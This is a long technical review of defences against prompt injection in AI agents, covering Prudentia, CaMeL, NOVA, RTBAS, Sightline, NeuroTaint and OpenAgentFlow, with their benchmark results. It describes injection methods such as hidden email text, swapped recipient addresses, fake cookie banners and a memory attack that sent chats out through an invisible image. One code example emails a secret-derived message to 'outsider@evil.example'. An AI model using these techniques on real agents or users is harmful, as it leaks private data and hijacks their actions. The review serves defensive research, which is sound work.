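- The description of each tool states its policy, and the model keeps track of its context's label. It can therefore predict which calls will need approval.
- Before opening a variable, the model has to call a planning tool. It writes down why it can't manage with the variable's name or a quarantined query, and which consequential calls it expects to make afterwards.
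- When the model opens a variable, it can ask the user to endorse the contents. If the user agrees, the text enters the context as trusted.

Under the instructions, the model should also make any consequential calls it can before it opens anything. This partly avoids the order problem in session taint, where an agent could send Dana a greeting before reading the emails but not afterwards.

The planning tool only records the plan, and no software evaluates whether the reasons in it are good. A bad plan usually means that the user has to give an extra approval or the agent fails its task. It can't get a forbidden call past the check, but it can lead the model to request an unnecessary endorsement, which the user might grant.

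In one run, a user asks for a summary of her appointments and then for a password reset link from a recent email. Because neither job needs a consequential call, the model opens the calendar descriptions without requesting endorsement. After a quarantined query fails, it opens the email too. The context is now untrusted, but the agent only has to show the user an answer, so she approves nothing, and requesting endorsement would have wasted her time.

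On tasks that don't depend on untrusted data, Kolluri and colleagues report up to 25% more tasks completed without approvals than with Fides, which they attribute to the planning step. On tasks that do, they report up to 2.5 times fewer approvals, which they attribute to the choice between endorsement and approval. These explanations are plausible, but they compared whole agents and didn't switch off one feature at a time, so they didn't measure each feature's effect.

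Prudentia's longer instructions and extra turns also cost money. With GPT-4o, tasks cost 3.9 to 6.3 cents on average, depending on the setting, compared with 1.5 to 3.3 cents for Fides and 0.4 to 1.1 cents for session taint. With o3-mini, banking tasks took 4.9 turns on average, compared with 2.0 under session taint. A few cents is still cheap if it saves someone an interruption. Kolluri and colleagues had not tried to reduce the cost.

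### One endorsement or ten approvals

Suppose a user asks her agent to complete a to-do list that a colleague has emailed her. The list has ten items, and each needs a consequential call. The email is untrusted, and the model has to read it to know what to do.

| | Open without endorsement | Open with endorsement |
|---|---|---|
| Context after reading | Untrusted | Trusted |
| Questions to the user | Ten, one before each call | One, before the model reads the email |
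| What the user judges | "May the agent do this?" | "Is this email safe to follow?" |
| An eleventh consequential call | Needs approval | Runs |

If the model expects to make *m* consequential calls after opening a text, approving each call requires *m* questions to the user, while endorsing the text requires one. Under Prudentia's instructions, the model asks for endorsement when *m* is greater than one. When *m* is one, either choice takes one question, and the model leaves the text unendorsed, which is safer because the user then approves a particular call.

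Endorsing the email reduces the number of approvals by giving its author much more power. Suppose the ninth item, written by an attacker, is to send the salary spreadsheet to an outside accountant. With ten approvals, the agent asks the user whether to send that file to that address, but with endorsement it sends the file without asking again. Since a trusted context is enough to send data to anyone, the user has in effect also given up the check on who may read her files.

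The instruction doesn't have to be on the list, either. An email can contain white text on a white background, or text below a long signature, that a person won't see but a model will read. Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that an approval screen needs careful design so that attackers can't manipulate what the user sees, but leave that design to later work. A maintainer who labels a GitHub issue as approved takes a similar risk, but usually has the issue open.

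Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, take the opposite approach. In their system, a person, a fixed rule or another model can authorise one exact call without changing the session's label. The permission doesn't carry over to the next call, so the to-do list would take ten decisions. Whoever deploys the system also limits what each authority may approve, for example by recipient. A tired user then can't approve sending salary data to an outsider if the limits exclude it. Kravchenko and colleagues report no successful attacks in 1,320 protected runs, but they used different benchmarks, so their results don't show which approach leads to fewer approval requests or better decisions.

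A designer could also show all ten proposed calls on one screen and let the user approve them together. The user would answer one question, as with endorsement, but would see the spreadsheet and its destination. This works only if the agent can specify every call in advance. If the third call depends on the result of the second, the user has to return to approve it.

### Whether people judge approvals correctly

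Kolluri and colleagues counted the calls after the experiments, in which no person approved anything, and assumed that a person would allow every harmless call and stop every attack.

Evidence from coding agents casts doubt on the assumption that people catch every attack. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, users approve 97% of the permission prompts in its coding agent. Most of those prompts are probably for safe, routine commands, so the figure alone doesn't prove carelessness. But the technology blog Hyrax reports that people in a test by Anthropic caught only 143 of 1,053 dangerous commands, or 13.6%. They stopped about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic was arguing for replacing manual prompts with its own automatic classifier, and commands in a terminal may be harder to judge than an email to a stranger. Still,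 the result would have to be wrong by a wide margin to support the assumption.

The drop during a session is an argument for labels, since fewer questions should leave people more alert. It is also a reason not to turn every blocked call into a question. Under session taint, an attack fails if the software blocks the planted call, but usually succeeds if the software instead asks a user who catches one dangerous call in seven. Hiding the planted text usually means the user is never asked, a benefit that the approval load doesn't measure.

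Asking people for fewer approvals may not make them more careful with the rest. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) surveyed developers and found that those who gave their agents more autonomy also approved actions without close review more often. This may be because people who trust their agents do both, in which case the survey doesn't show that autonomy causes carelessness.

The content of the approval prompt also matters. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of incidents with agents and found that the user's review played a part in 105. In 80 of those, users had turned on automatic approval, often because the alternative was hundreds of prompts per session. In 31, the prompt showed a command without its effects. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) points out that the action itself may not contain the information a person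 needs. A request to post a comment looks routine unless the user learns that the comment's text came from a private file. Labels could supply that information, and Kolluri and colleagues suggest showing them in the prompt, along with the data's origin, because an attacker can't alter them.

The approval load would be more informative alongside a measure of how well people decide. *Agent Reliability Profiles in Financial Services* (2026) recommends recording approval times and refusal rates, and occasionally testing reviewers with a wrong but harmless proposal that the software will block even if they approve it. If reviewers approve it, the agent is more autonomous than its settings suggest.

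### Runs that fail and questions that remain

Kolluri and colleagues exclude failed runs from the approval load because a user would probably refuse some calls and give up. In most of the failed runs, the agent kept trying actions that broke the policy. But a real user would answer a few approval requests before losing patience, and *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) notes that agents are designed to look for another route after a refusal, which can lead to more requests. With o3-mini, 30% to 38% of tasks failed even with unlimited approvals, so the omission could be large.

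An agent that fails more tasks can therefore appear to need fewer approvals. With GPT-4o, Fides had a load of 7.8, against 39.4 for session taint, but it completed 56.3% of the tasks, against 72.2%. Dividing the load by the number of completed tasks doesn't correct for this, because the tasks that Fides failed may be the ones that would have needed approvals. TCR@k is a better measure because failures lower it. Fides leads session taint by about 12 points when no approvals are allowed, and session taint leads by 12 points when each task is allowed at most one.

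The counts also cover only approvals that protect against attacks. Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that labels can't replace approvals meant to catch the model's own mistakes. If a bank requires a person to confirm every payment in case the agent gets the amount wrong, the bank will still need that confirmation when every label is trusted.

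## CaMeL and plans fixed before untrusted data is read

Fides and Prudentia choose one tool call at a time, and their main model can open a hidden text if it gets stuck. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, a March 2025 Google DeepMind paper by Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, presented CaMeL (CApabilities for MachinE Learning), which removes that option. CaMeL's privileged model writes the whole job as a program before any tool runs, using only the user's request and the tool descriptions. This prevents planted text from changing the plan, but it also prevents the agent from revising the plan when it reads something useful.

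### Sending Bob his document

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, describes the CaMeL paper's main example. A user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested in their last meeting, and says the meeting notes contain Bob's address and the document's name. In Willison's own Dual LLM pattern, the privileged model plans the right steps, and the quarantined model reads the notes and returns the address. But anyone who can edit the notes can substitute their own address, and the assistant then emails them the document. The attacker changes a value in the plan without adding a step, and the pattern doesn't check values.

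CaMeL's privileged model would write something like this:

```
notes    = find_meeting_notes()
address  = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's email address", notes, email_address)
name     = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes, text)
document = fetch_document(name)
send_email(recipient=address, subject="Your document", attachment=document)
```

A custom interpreter runs the program and calls the tools. It attaches *capabilities* to every value, which are a record of where the value came from and who may read it. Suppose Bob and Dana already have access to both the notes and the document:

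| Value | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| `address` | Meeting notes | User, Bob, Dana |
| `document` | Document store, and the notes through `name` | User, Bob, Dana |
| Subject line | The program itself | Anyone |

Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe these policies as Python functions that receive the call, its arguments and their capabilities, then allow or deny the call and give a reason. A policy for `send_email` could allow a message if the recipient's address came from the user, or if the recipient may already read everything in the message. An attacker who edits the notes then gets these results:

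| Change to the notes | Result |
|---|---|
| An added order to forward all the user's mail | Nothing, because no line of the program forwards mail |
| The attacker's address in place of Bob's | The address didn't come from the user and isn't a permitted reader, so the software blocks the email or asks the user |
| The salary spreadsheet in place of Bob's document | Bob isn't a permitted reader, so the software blocks the email or asks the user |
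| An outdated contract that Bob may read | The email goes out |

The honest request can also fail if Bob asked for the document because he has no access to it. The user then has to approve the email.

### Normal and strict tracking

Each line of a program names its inputs, so the interpreter can work out the label of `document` from the label of `name`, much as Perl does with strings. Decisions are harder to track. Suppose a user asks the agent to warn Dana once for each urgent email:

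```
for email in read_emails(number=10):
    urgent = ask_quarantined("Is this urgent?", email, yes_no)
    if urgent:
        send_message(to="Dana", text="Please check the inbox")
```

The privileged model wrote the warning's recipient and text. In *normal* mode, the interpreter tracks only the data that goes into a value, so the call counts as trusted even though strangers decide how many warnings Dana gets. In *strict* mode, anything inside an `if` also takes the labels of the condition, and anything inside a `for` loop takes the labels of the list it runs through. The warning then carries the labels of the emails, so a policy that requires trusted inputs blocks it.

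Strict mode catches this implicit flow but marks more harmless values as untrusted. Even a constant assigned inside the loop, as in `status = "done"`, becomes untrusted. Strict mode still taints less than session taint does, because a message after the loop that uses nothing from inside it remains trusted.

The choice of mode has made little difference on AgentDojo. *Language-Based Agent Control* ran CaMeL in both modes on the Slack tasks and found all the results within 4% of each other. One likely reason is that programs for this benchmark seldom branch on what they read. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) counted an average of 3.7 branches per AgentDojo program and found that 79.4% of the branches depended only on values internal to the plan.

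CaMeL still misses some flows. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, point out that it raises a variable's label only in the branch that the program actually takes. In this version of their example, `balance` is secret:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000:  tmp  = False
if tmp:              rich = False
if rich:             send_email("outsider@evil.example", "rich!")
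```

If the balance is large, the first condition makes `tmp` false and secret. The program skips the line that would have changed `rich`, which stays true and public, and sends the email. If the balance is small, `rich` becomes false and the program sends no email. In both cases `rich` reveals the secret without carrying its label, which is the problem Austin and Flanagan describe in ordinary code.

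An attacker can't write such a program because only the privileged model writes programs, so this leak occurs only if that model happens to write one. Garby and colleagues found another fault that is more worrying in practice. When a program inserts an untrusted value into a longer string, the interpreter treats the value as trusted. Programs routinely build strings this way, so a sentence planted by an attacker could get past a policy.

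Retries are another weak point. If a program crashes, CaMeL returns the error to the privileged model, which writes a new program. CaMeL censors error messages to limit how much information from untrusted data reaches the model. But the retry loop runs outside the interpreter, so each new program starts with clean labels even though it responds to what happened in the last one. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit about a secret, and Garby and colleagues note that repeated attempts can reveal the rest. If a program fails halfway, the retry may also repeat actions already taken, such as sending an email.

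### Results with and without policies

Debenedetti and colleagues first reported that CaMeL solved 67% of AgentDojo's tasks with its security guarantees. Their June 2025 revision raised this to 77%, compared with 84% for an unprotected agent. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that, with GPT-4o, CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens on the median task as an agent with no defence, the highest token overhead of any defence in the comparison.

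Later tests by other researchers, using newer models, got much lower completion rates when they turned the policies on. Garby and colleagues ran the 16 banking tasks three times each, and *Language-Based Agent Control* ran the 21 Slack tasks:

| Setting | Model | Policies off | Policies on |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Banking | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 37.5% |
| Slack | Opus 4.7 | 71.4% | 23.8% |
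| Slack | Opus 4.8 | 76.2% | 28.6% |
| Slack | GPT 5.4 | 81.0% | 23.8% |
| Slack | Sonnet 5 | 61.9% | 19.0% |

With policies on, these figures are close to the 37.5% in banking and 17% to 20% in Slack that Costa and colleagues measured for plain session taint. The models and policies differed, so the match may be partly a coincidence. But tracking every value evidently doesn't save many tasks when the policies forbid what the user asked for. Garby and colleagues report that *Language-Based Agent Control* attributes many of the losses to tasks with flows that no secure policy would allow, and suggests asking the user to confirm those flows.

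*SecureClaw* (2026) ran an adapted copy of CaMeL on the whole benchmark. When not under attack, it completed 29 of 97 tasks, and none of 629 attacks succeeded. Part of the shortfall against the CaMeL paper's 77% may come from the adaptation. All three groups were also promoting their own designs, so they had less reason to tune CaMeL. Even so, the "comparable task performance" that *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) credits to CaMeL looks too generous for an agent running with nobody there to override its policies.

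The fixed plan provides most of CaMeL's security. Garby and colleagues sorted the 144 pairs of banking task and attack by whether the attack could succeed within a reasonable program for the task. In 97 pairs, the attack needed a call that such a program would never contain, such as a payment during a request to summarise recent transactions. Five attacks succeeded in the 622 runs that finished with policies off, and none succeeded with policies on, but CaMeL then completed only a little over half as many harmless tasks.

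The policies look barely worthwhile in that comparison, but the result could be different against a real attacker. The benchmark's attacks are mostly meant to make the agent take an extra action. A fixed plan doesn't stop the agent from paying an altered bill, like the one in the Fides example, because the payment needs no extra call.

In two of the five successes, the user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop that looked up each instruction in the file and called the matching tool, so whoever wrote the file could choose the agent's actions despite the fixed plan.

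Garby and colleagues' agent, Randori, keeps its checks on but lets the privileged model endorse particular values in its program, before any outside data arrives. It also practises on simulated tools, so it can correct mistakes without using the real tools. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 75% of the banking tasks. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded, both in a task that told the agent to make a payment as instructed in a text file. The agent had to endorse the file's contents to do what the user asked, and this also let the forged version through.

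### What a fixed plan can't do

A plan written beforehand fails when the next step depends on what the agent reads. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) found in *AgentDyn* that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to replan. Costa and colleagues' classification implies that 20 tasks can't be completed unless the main model reads untrusted text, so the count depends on the criterion. By either count, these tasks are a minority, so AgentDojo favors CaMeL.

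Li and colleagues therefore built a benchmark of 60 shopping, GitHub and everyday tasks. Every task needs replanning and includes a helpful instruction from a third party, such as a checkout page's request that the customer log in first. The tasks take 7.1 steps on average, compared with 3.5 in AgentDojo. Li and colleagues report severe losses for CaMeL and the other defences that rely on an initial plan.

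As in the multi-agent tests, the program can also contain wrong assumptions about data that the privileged model hasn't seen. For example, a line that compares two dates may crash if the calendar tool returns them in a format that the tool's description doesn't mention.

CaMeL doesn't protect the content of permitted fields either, as with the outdated contract. Garby and colleagues explain that both successful attacks in Debenedetti and colleagues' evaluation were of this general kind. One was a payment that followed a document's instructions, which the CaMeL paper places outside its threat model. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the benchmark counted this as a successful attack.

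Someone also has to write CaMeL's policies and keep them up to date, a burden Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge. Willison welcomed CaMeL as the first credible defence he had seen that didn't rely on more AI, but he was nervous about the policies. After two decades in application security, he still found Amazon's system of access permissions hard to work out.

Policies also take effect late, because the interpreter checks each call only when the program reaches it. Nikolaou and colleagues describe a security team's agent that investigates an alert at length and then tries to cut a computer off from the network without the required approval, which wastes all the earlier work. CaMeLoT, their extension, translates the program into a finite set of states and checks the rules before running anything. If it finds a path that breaks a rule, it sends the path to the privileged model, which can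 add the missing approval step. CaMeLoT can't determine how often a loop will run, so it allows for any number of passes and may reject some safe programs.

### Plans for a screen the planner can't see

Agents that operate a computer through its screen look like the worst case for a fixed plan, since each click depends on what is showing. Foerster and colleagues argue that screens are more predictable than they seem. Their method, NOVA (Navigating via Observation, Verification, and Action), has the privileged model write branches for the screens that might appear:

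```
screen = describe_screen()
if verify_hypothesis("a cookie banner is visible", screen):
    click(find("button that closes the banner"))
```

A quarantined vision model describes the screen and finds the coordinates of buttons. A second quarantined call compares the description with the prediction and returns yes or no, and the interpreter takes the matching branch. The privileged model never sees the screen or the answers.

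An average NOVA program has 213 lines, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, 5 tool calls and 4 branches for an AgentDojo task. About half of the steps are fallbacks that don't run.

Foerster and colleagues tested NOVA on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in ordinary desktop applications such as Chrome and LibreOffice. Of the tasks each model solved without isolation, the table shows how many it still solved with NOVA.

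| Model operating the screen | Solved without isolation | Solved with NOVA in one attempt | Solved in at least one of five attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS-1.5-7B | 60 | 25 (41.7%) | 39 (65.0%) |
| OpenCUA-32B | 76 | 22 (28.9%) | 48 (63.2%) |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 | 31 (28.4%) | 62 (56.9%) |

The paper's claim that NOVA retains up to 57% of a frontier model's performance rests on the last figure in the table. That figure holds only if somebody can tell which of five attempts worked, and an agent that books flights can't make five attempts on the user's real account. The baseline without isolation was also low. Claude Sonnet 4.5 scored 37.7%, against a published 58.1%, because Foerster and colleagues limited it to 15 steps instead of 50.

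The claim that small models improve by up to 19% has a similar problem. UI-TARS's score over the whole benchmark rose from 24.4% to 29.0%, but the second figure is the best of three attempts. On a single attempt with NOVA, UI-TARS solved 51 of the 339 tasks the benchmark can score automatically, fewer than the 60 it solved without isolation.

Still, these results are better than one might expect from a planner that can't see the screen. Without NOVA's instructions, the same CaMeL design solved only 4 of UI-TARS's 60 tasks in one attempt. Fixing the plan in advance also used far fewer tokens. Foerster and colleagues report a token overhead of 1.88 times for CaMeL and 29.6 times for a version built on Fides, which calls the planner again at every step with the full history. Both solved about two thirds of the 60 tasks within five attempts.

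NOVA only partly solves the replanning problem, because the privileged model has to foresee each screen. Attackers can also try to influence each branch, which Foerster and colleagues call *Branch Steering*. In one attack, an advertisement imitates a cookie banner, the vision model reports a banner, and the program clicks through to the attacker's site. Checking the screenshot against the page's underlying structure stopped this attack for static Google advertisements but not for HTML5 ones. Having a second model check the first couldn't reliably stop it without also rejecting legitimate banners. In another attack, small changes to an advertisement's pixels got past both checks.

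Foerster and colleagues ran all of this without policies, because you can't tell from a call such as `click(412, 230)` whether it closes a banner or deletes a file. Strict tracking would not have helped much. Nearly every click is inside a branch that depends on the screen, so strict tracking would mark nearly every click untrusted, as session taint does.

### Engineering cost and adoption

CaMeL needs its own interpreter, which supports only part of Python. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) notes that programs can't define their own functions or use recursion, and contrasts this with its own system, which uses the standard Scala 3 compiler. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) left CaMeL out of one benchmark because fitting CaMeL's interpreter and benchmark-specific policies into the test setup would have meant replacing the core of the defence. A company with several agents would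 have to write policies for each agent's tools. If the agents cooperate, the system would also need a way to pass labels between them, as multi-CaMeL does.

The quarantined calls add delay. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) estimated from GPT-4's response times that reviewing ten emails could take more than ten seconds. It recommends ordinary parsers for structured data such as JSON, and reports that parsers combined with caching cut tokens and delay by up to half in internal tests, but gives no details of those tests. Quarantine can also protect privacy, because if a company runs a small quarantined model on its own machines, the provider of the privileged model never sees the user's documents.

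In May 2026, McKerchar wrote in *Inside the lethal trifecta*, an article for the security company Sophos, that no production-grade implementation of CaMeL existed and that no mainstream agent product had adopted it or the Dual LLM pattern. He named Claude Code, Cursor, Hermes, GitHub Copilot Agent and Gemini CLI among the products that had not. Microsoft's experimental integrations are a partial exception, but they follow Fides and choose calls one at a time.

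CaMeL was still research software in autumn 2026. CaMeLoT, from September, extends the published code, and *Evolution Under Fire*, from November, tested the official research copy. Shumailov, one of CaMeL's designers, now gives his affiliation as the AI Sequrity Company, which suggests commercial interest but isn't evidence that anyone uses the design in a product.

Most of the products on McKerchar's list are coding agents, which helps explain the gap. A coding agent runs a test, reads the error and decides what to change next, and a program written before the test ran can't do that. McKerchar advises security teams not to wait for such designs and to limit the damage a hijacked agent can do, for example by isolating its credentials and restricting its network access.

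## Estimating which inputs influenced a model's output

Hidden variables, quarantined models and fixed plans all keep untrusted text away from the model that picks the actions. Some agents, including coding agents, sometimes need that model to read the text. If the model has to read everything, a designer who still wants value labels must estimate which inputs influenced each output and drop the labels of the other inputs.

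Such an estimate helps only when some inputs had no effect. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) measured how often that happens in ordinary programs that insert data into a prompt and call a model. In code from 2,103 families of open-source projects, 12–14% of the inserted pieces had no visible effect on the output's wording or on any decision in it. The share is probably larger for an agent that has read many emails and then sends a greeting.

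### Generating the answer again from fewer inputs

Siddiqui and colleagues proposed a cautious method. As Costa and colleagues describe it, the software works out which messages influenced the model's response, generates a new response from those messages alone, and gives that response the join of the messages' labels. Costa and colleagues report that the new response is about as useful as one generated from the full context.

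The search requires a lot of computation. Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *RTBAS*, explain that the basic version tries subsets of the inputs to find the smallest one that gives a similar output, and ten documents have 1,024 subsets. A faster version searches over the levels of the label scale and adds 16 to 64 model calls for a scale with four to six levels. The method labels the final answer but doesn't check tool calls against a policy.

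RTBAS, an agent framework by Zhong and colleagues, replaces the search with a single screening step and adds the policy check. It divides the history into regions, each of which is a message or part of one and has an integrity label and a confidentiality label.

```
before each model call:
    relevant = screener(all regions in the history)
    label    = join of the labels of the relevant regions
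    mask every region whose label is not at or below label
    calls    = model(masked history)

for each call:
    if the tool's policy does not permit label:  ask the user
    if the call runs:  result's label = join(label, tool's label)
```

Session taint blocks the "Good morning" message to Dana once the agent has read the user's emails. Under RTBAS, the emails are also in the history, but the screener should find that the greeting doesn't depend on them. The software then masks the emails, the model writes the greeting from the user's request, and the call goes out as trusted.

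The masking follows labels, so a region can stay visible even if the screener found it irrelevant. Trusted, public text always stays visible. If the screener picks one untrusted public web page, every other untrusted public page stays visible too, because none of them would raise the label.

Zhong and colleagues built two screeners. One puts numbered markers around the regions and asks a second model which regions the next step needs. The other lets the agent's model write a draft from the full history, then computes *attention scores*, which estimate how much harder each word of the draft would have been to predict without a given piece of the input. The agent's model, GPT-4o, doesn't expose its internals, so a small open model computes the scores, and a small neural network turns them into a yes or no for each region. The network was right 81% of the time on test data.

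On AgentDojo, RTBAS stopped every attack that broke its policy, across 629 combinations of task and attack. In one case the planted instruction was in text that carried the user's trusted label, so the labels could not catch it. Without attacks, task completion fell by 10% with the judging model and by 7.4% with attention scores. These figures come from runs in which the software skipped forbidden calls without asking anyone. Completion fell most on the Slack tasks, to 22% with the judging model and 33% with attention scores, because many of them tell the agent to act on content from an untrusted website. Zhong and colleagues trained the attention screener on 40 cases from AgentDojo itself, so its results there may overstate how well it works.

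Zhong and colleagues also wrote 37 tasks about accidental leaks, in which an agent for payments, flights or shopping has private data in its history. The judging model caused an unnecessary question in three tasks and hid data that the agent needed in four. Attention scores also hid needed data in four tasks but caused six unnecessary questions, compared with eleven when the software asked every time. For each tool call, the researchers checked whether the label named exactly the right kinds of private data. The judging model got 70% of the labels right. Attention scores got 57.3%, hardly better than the 56.7% from assuming that every secret leaks.

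The screening roughly doubled cost and time. A banking task cost 1.5 cents and took 4.4 seconds without protection. It cost 2.8 cents and took 8.7 seconds with attention scores, and 3.2 cents and 9.7 seconds with the judging model.

### What the excluded inputs can still change

Zhong and colleagues argue that a screener's mistakes can't compromise security. If the screener wrongly leaves out an email, the model never sees it when writing the call, so an order planted in the email can't influence the call. The task usually fails because the model lacks something it needed. If the screener wrongly includes an email, the label rises and the user gets an extra question.

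If the software keeps the original answer and only estimates which inputs shaped it, a wrong estimate puts a clean label on an action that an attacker influenced. Generating the answer again avoids this error, which is its main advantage.

The argument has a gap because the screener reads everything. Suppose a user asks her agent to pay the rent at the amount on file unless the landlord has written with a new one. The landlord has written, but a stranger's email causes the screener to conclude wrongly that no message concerns the payment. The software masks all the mail, the agent's model pays the old amount, and the payment counts as trusted. The stranger has changed the outcome through an implicit flow. With two levels for each kind of label, the screener's verdict has only four possible values, so it can pass at most two bits to each model call.

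Siddiqui and colleagues' basic version leaves an untrusted source more room to influence the answer, because it selects individual documents. Suppose an assistant has two trusted price lists, one of them out of date, and a stranger's page with an instruction to use the old one. The answer generated from all three documents quotes the old price. The search looks for a small set of documents that gives a similar answer, finds the old list, and labels the answer generated from that list trusted. That answer contains none of the stranger's text, but the stranger's instruction determined which list it came from.

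### How well the signals track influence

Any judgement of relevance relies on some signal, and the common signals fail in different ways. In a transformer, the design behind most current language models, information moves from one position in the text to another only through attention. Xu and colleagues prove that, to a first approximation, input that gets no attention can't affect the output. But every input gets at least a little attention. A model can also attend heavily to something it doesn't use, such as a line of dashes between two documents, and an input that gets only faint attention can still decide the answer.

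*GIF* instead measures how much small changes to the model's internal representation of an input would shift the probabilities of its next words. This works badly when the model is nearly certain. If it is 99.9% sure that the answer is "yes", a small change to an input's representation hardly moves the probability, even if that input is the only reason for the answer. Xu and colleagues found that one in five outputs of the open model Qwen3-8B left less than 1% of the probability to other words. Many decisions that matter for an agent's security, such as whether to pay an invoice, are short, confident answers.

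Removing an input and checking whether the output changes fails when another input repeats the same content. Xu and colleagues found that, with duplicated content, this method scored 54.0 to 68.8 on a scale where 50 is guessing and 100 is perfect.

Sightline reads the model's attention and learns from labelled examples which attention patterns show that the model used an input. It sets its cut-off to miss no more than a chosen share of real influences on average. With the limit at 1%, it missed about 1% of them and removed 43.9% to 65.6% of the unnecessary data labels, depending on the model. It needs one extra pass through the model, which takes 0.12 to 0.20 seconds. In a test on an agent, it removed about half of the unnecessary labels, and no attack got past the integrity policy.

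The 1% limit holds when new calls resemble the ones used to set the cut-off. An attacker deliberately writes unusual text and can try many versions, so an average over ordinary programs is a poor guide to how often a determined attacker would go undetected. Sightline labels the original output, so each miss leaves an influenced output with a clean label.

### NeuroTaint's audit after the fact

NeuroTaint, the tool presented in *Ghost in the Agent*, works from a log of what the agent read, saved and did. The user lists the tools that bring in untrusted content, such as a web search, and the tools whose effects matter, such as sending email. For each call to one of the latter, NeuroTaint looks for traces of earlier untrusted content in the arguments:

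1. It adds a random marker to each untrusted result as it arrives, and checks whether the marker turns up in the call.
2. It measures how much of the wording overlaps.
3. It compares the meaning of the two texts numerically, to catch paraphrases and translations.
4. It repeats the comparison with short chunks of the source, because one planted sentence barely affects the overall meaning of a long page.

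If it finds no trace, it replaces the untrusted result with neutral text in a copy of the history and asks a model whether the agent would still have made the call. For example, suppose a planted "policy update" makes an agent forward a customer's message to an outside address. The comparisons may find nothing because the message contains nothing from the update, but the agent would have had no reason to forward it without the update.

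NeuroTaint's developers tested it on TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios they wrote across 20 agent frameworks. Untrusted content reaches or influences a sensitive call in half of them. NeuroTaint found 187 of those 200 cases and raised 16 false alarms. It found every case with copied wording, 75 of the 85 that required comparing meaning, and 37 of the 40 that required judging whether the call would have happened without the untrusted content. Most false alarms came from outputs that were on the same topic as an untrusted page but didn't draw on it.

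These numbers are probably optimistic. The developers wrote both the tool and the benchmark, and the test set-up uses a much stricter similarity threshold for "safe-control policies" (0.95) than for ordinary comparisons (0.60). If those policies belong to the harmless scenarios, the set-up gave the tool information about the right answer, and false alarms would be more common in practice.

The comparison with Fides is also weak evidence. The Fides baseline found 108 of the 200 cases and raised 106 false alarms, but 40 of its 92 misses came from four of the 20 frameworks, where it flagged nothing. That looks more like a problem with the adaptation than with labels. Session taint that kept its labels in memory would, by construction, flag all 200 cases, but it would also flag many of the harmless ones.

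An attacker who knew that the method removes sources one at a time could plant the same instruction in two web pages. The agent would still make the call if only one page were removed, so the method may attribute the call to neither page. The model that makes this attribution also reads the original history, including the planted text.

### Matching outgoing text against earlier values

*OpenAgentFlow* (Chen, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes a simpler form of tracking that can stop a call before it runs. The software sits between a group of agents and all the tools they use. When a protected source returns a value, the software records the value, its kind and its source. Before any later action, it extracts the fields of the outgoing text, puts them in a standard form and looks for a match with the recorded values. If one agent looks up a phone number in the contacts and another puts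 it in an email, the software can match the number without relying on either agent to report its origin.

Matching works best for values with a fixed form, such as phone numbers and account numbers. If an agent reads that Dana earns 61,040 and writes that she earns "a little over sixty thousand", a search for the exact figure will miss the connection. It will also miss the connection between ten salaries and their total. Common values can cause false matches, since an amount of 100 may appear in two places by coincidence. Chen and colleagues add that the tracking covers only the points where the software can observe values.

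OpenAgentFlow therefore backs up matching with fixed rules, a check of meaning and a final review of unresolved cases. On 1,220 recorded cases based on AgentDojo, it caught 96.59% of unsafe actions and interfered with 1.96% of safe ones. On 300 cases that Chen and colleagues built, it blocked 95.35% of attacks. These figures are for all four stages together, so they don't show how much the matching contributed.

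The table compares what happens when each method misjudges an input.

| Method | What the model saw when it produced the final action | If the method misses an influential input | If it reports a harmless input |
|---|---|---|---|
| Siddiqui and colleagues | Only the selected inputs | The answer lacks something it needed | The answer gets a stricter label |
| RTBAS | Inputs at or below the chosen label | The task may fail | The user gets an extra question |
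| NeuroTaint | Everything | The audit passes an attack that has already happened | An investigator follows a false lead |
| OpenAgentFlow | Everything | The action runs unless another stage stops it | The software may block or question a safe action |

### Labels on what an agent remembers

Memory makes all of these estimates harder because errors persist after the session ends. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on the ChatGPT app for Mac in which a web page or document planted an instruction in the app's long-term memory. From then on, the app sent the user's conversations to the attacker's server, hidden in the address of an invisible image. The app treated its memory as a trusted record of the user's preferences, although the attacker had written part of it.

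*AgentKernel* (Zou, Guo and colleagues, 2026) proposes an operating system for agents that labels each item in memory and updates the labels as the agent combines items. In its example, a stranger's comment on a proposed code change contains a planted instruction. A reviewing agent saves a summary of the comment, and a second agent later retrieves the summary as trusted and deploys malicious code. The paper offers a design, a security analysis and a comparison with other products, but lists no experiment among its contributions. The case for item labels depends on a single session label being too coarse for memory and on item labels being accurate enough to replace it.

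The join rule supports the claim about session labels. Suppose an agent reads one web page on Monday and then saves five notes, including the user's seating preference for flights. Under session taint, all five notes are labeled untrusted. On Tuesday the agent recalls the seating preference, which taints the new session and every note the agent then writes. After a few weeks, nearly everything in memory is labeled untrusted.

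Even so, the agent would remain usable when someone is present to approve its actions. At worst, a session that starts untrusted needs approval for every consequential action. An agent that always asks for approval, tested by Kolluri and colleagues, completed over half of AgentDojo's tasks with at most one approval each. An unattended agent would lose far more of its usefulness. Ouyang and Hou (2026) accept in *MemLineage* that coarse rules for memory can be effective, but object that such rules treat a useful note and a dangerous one alike.

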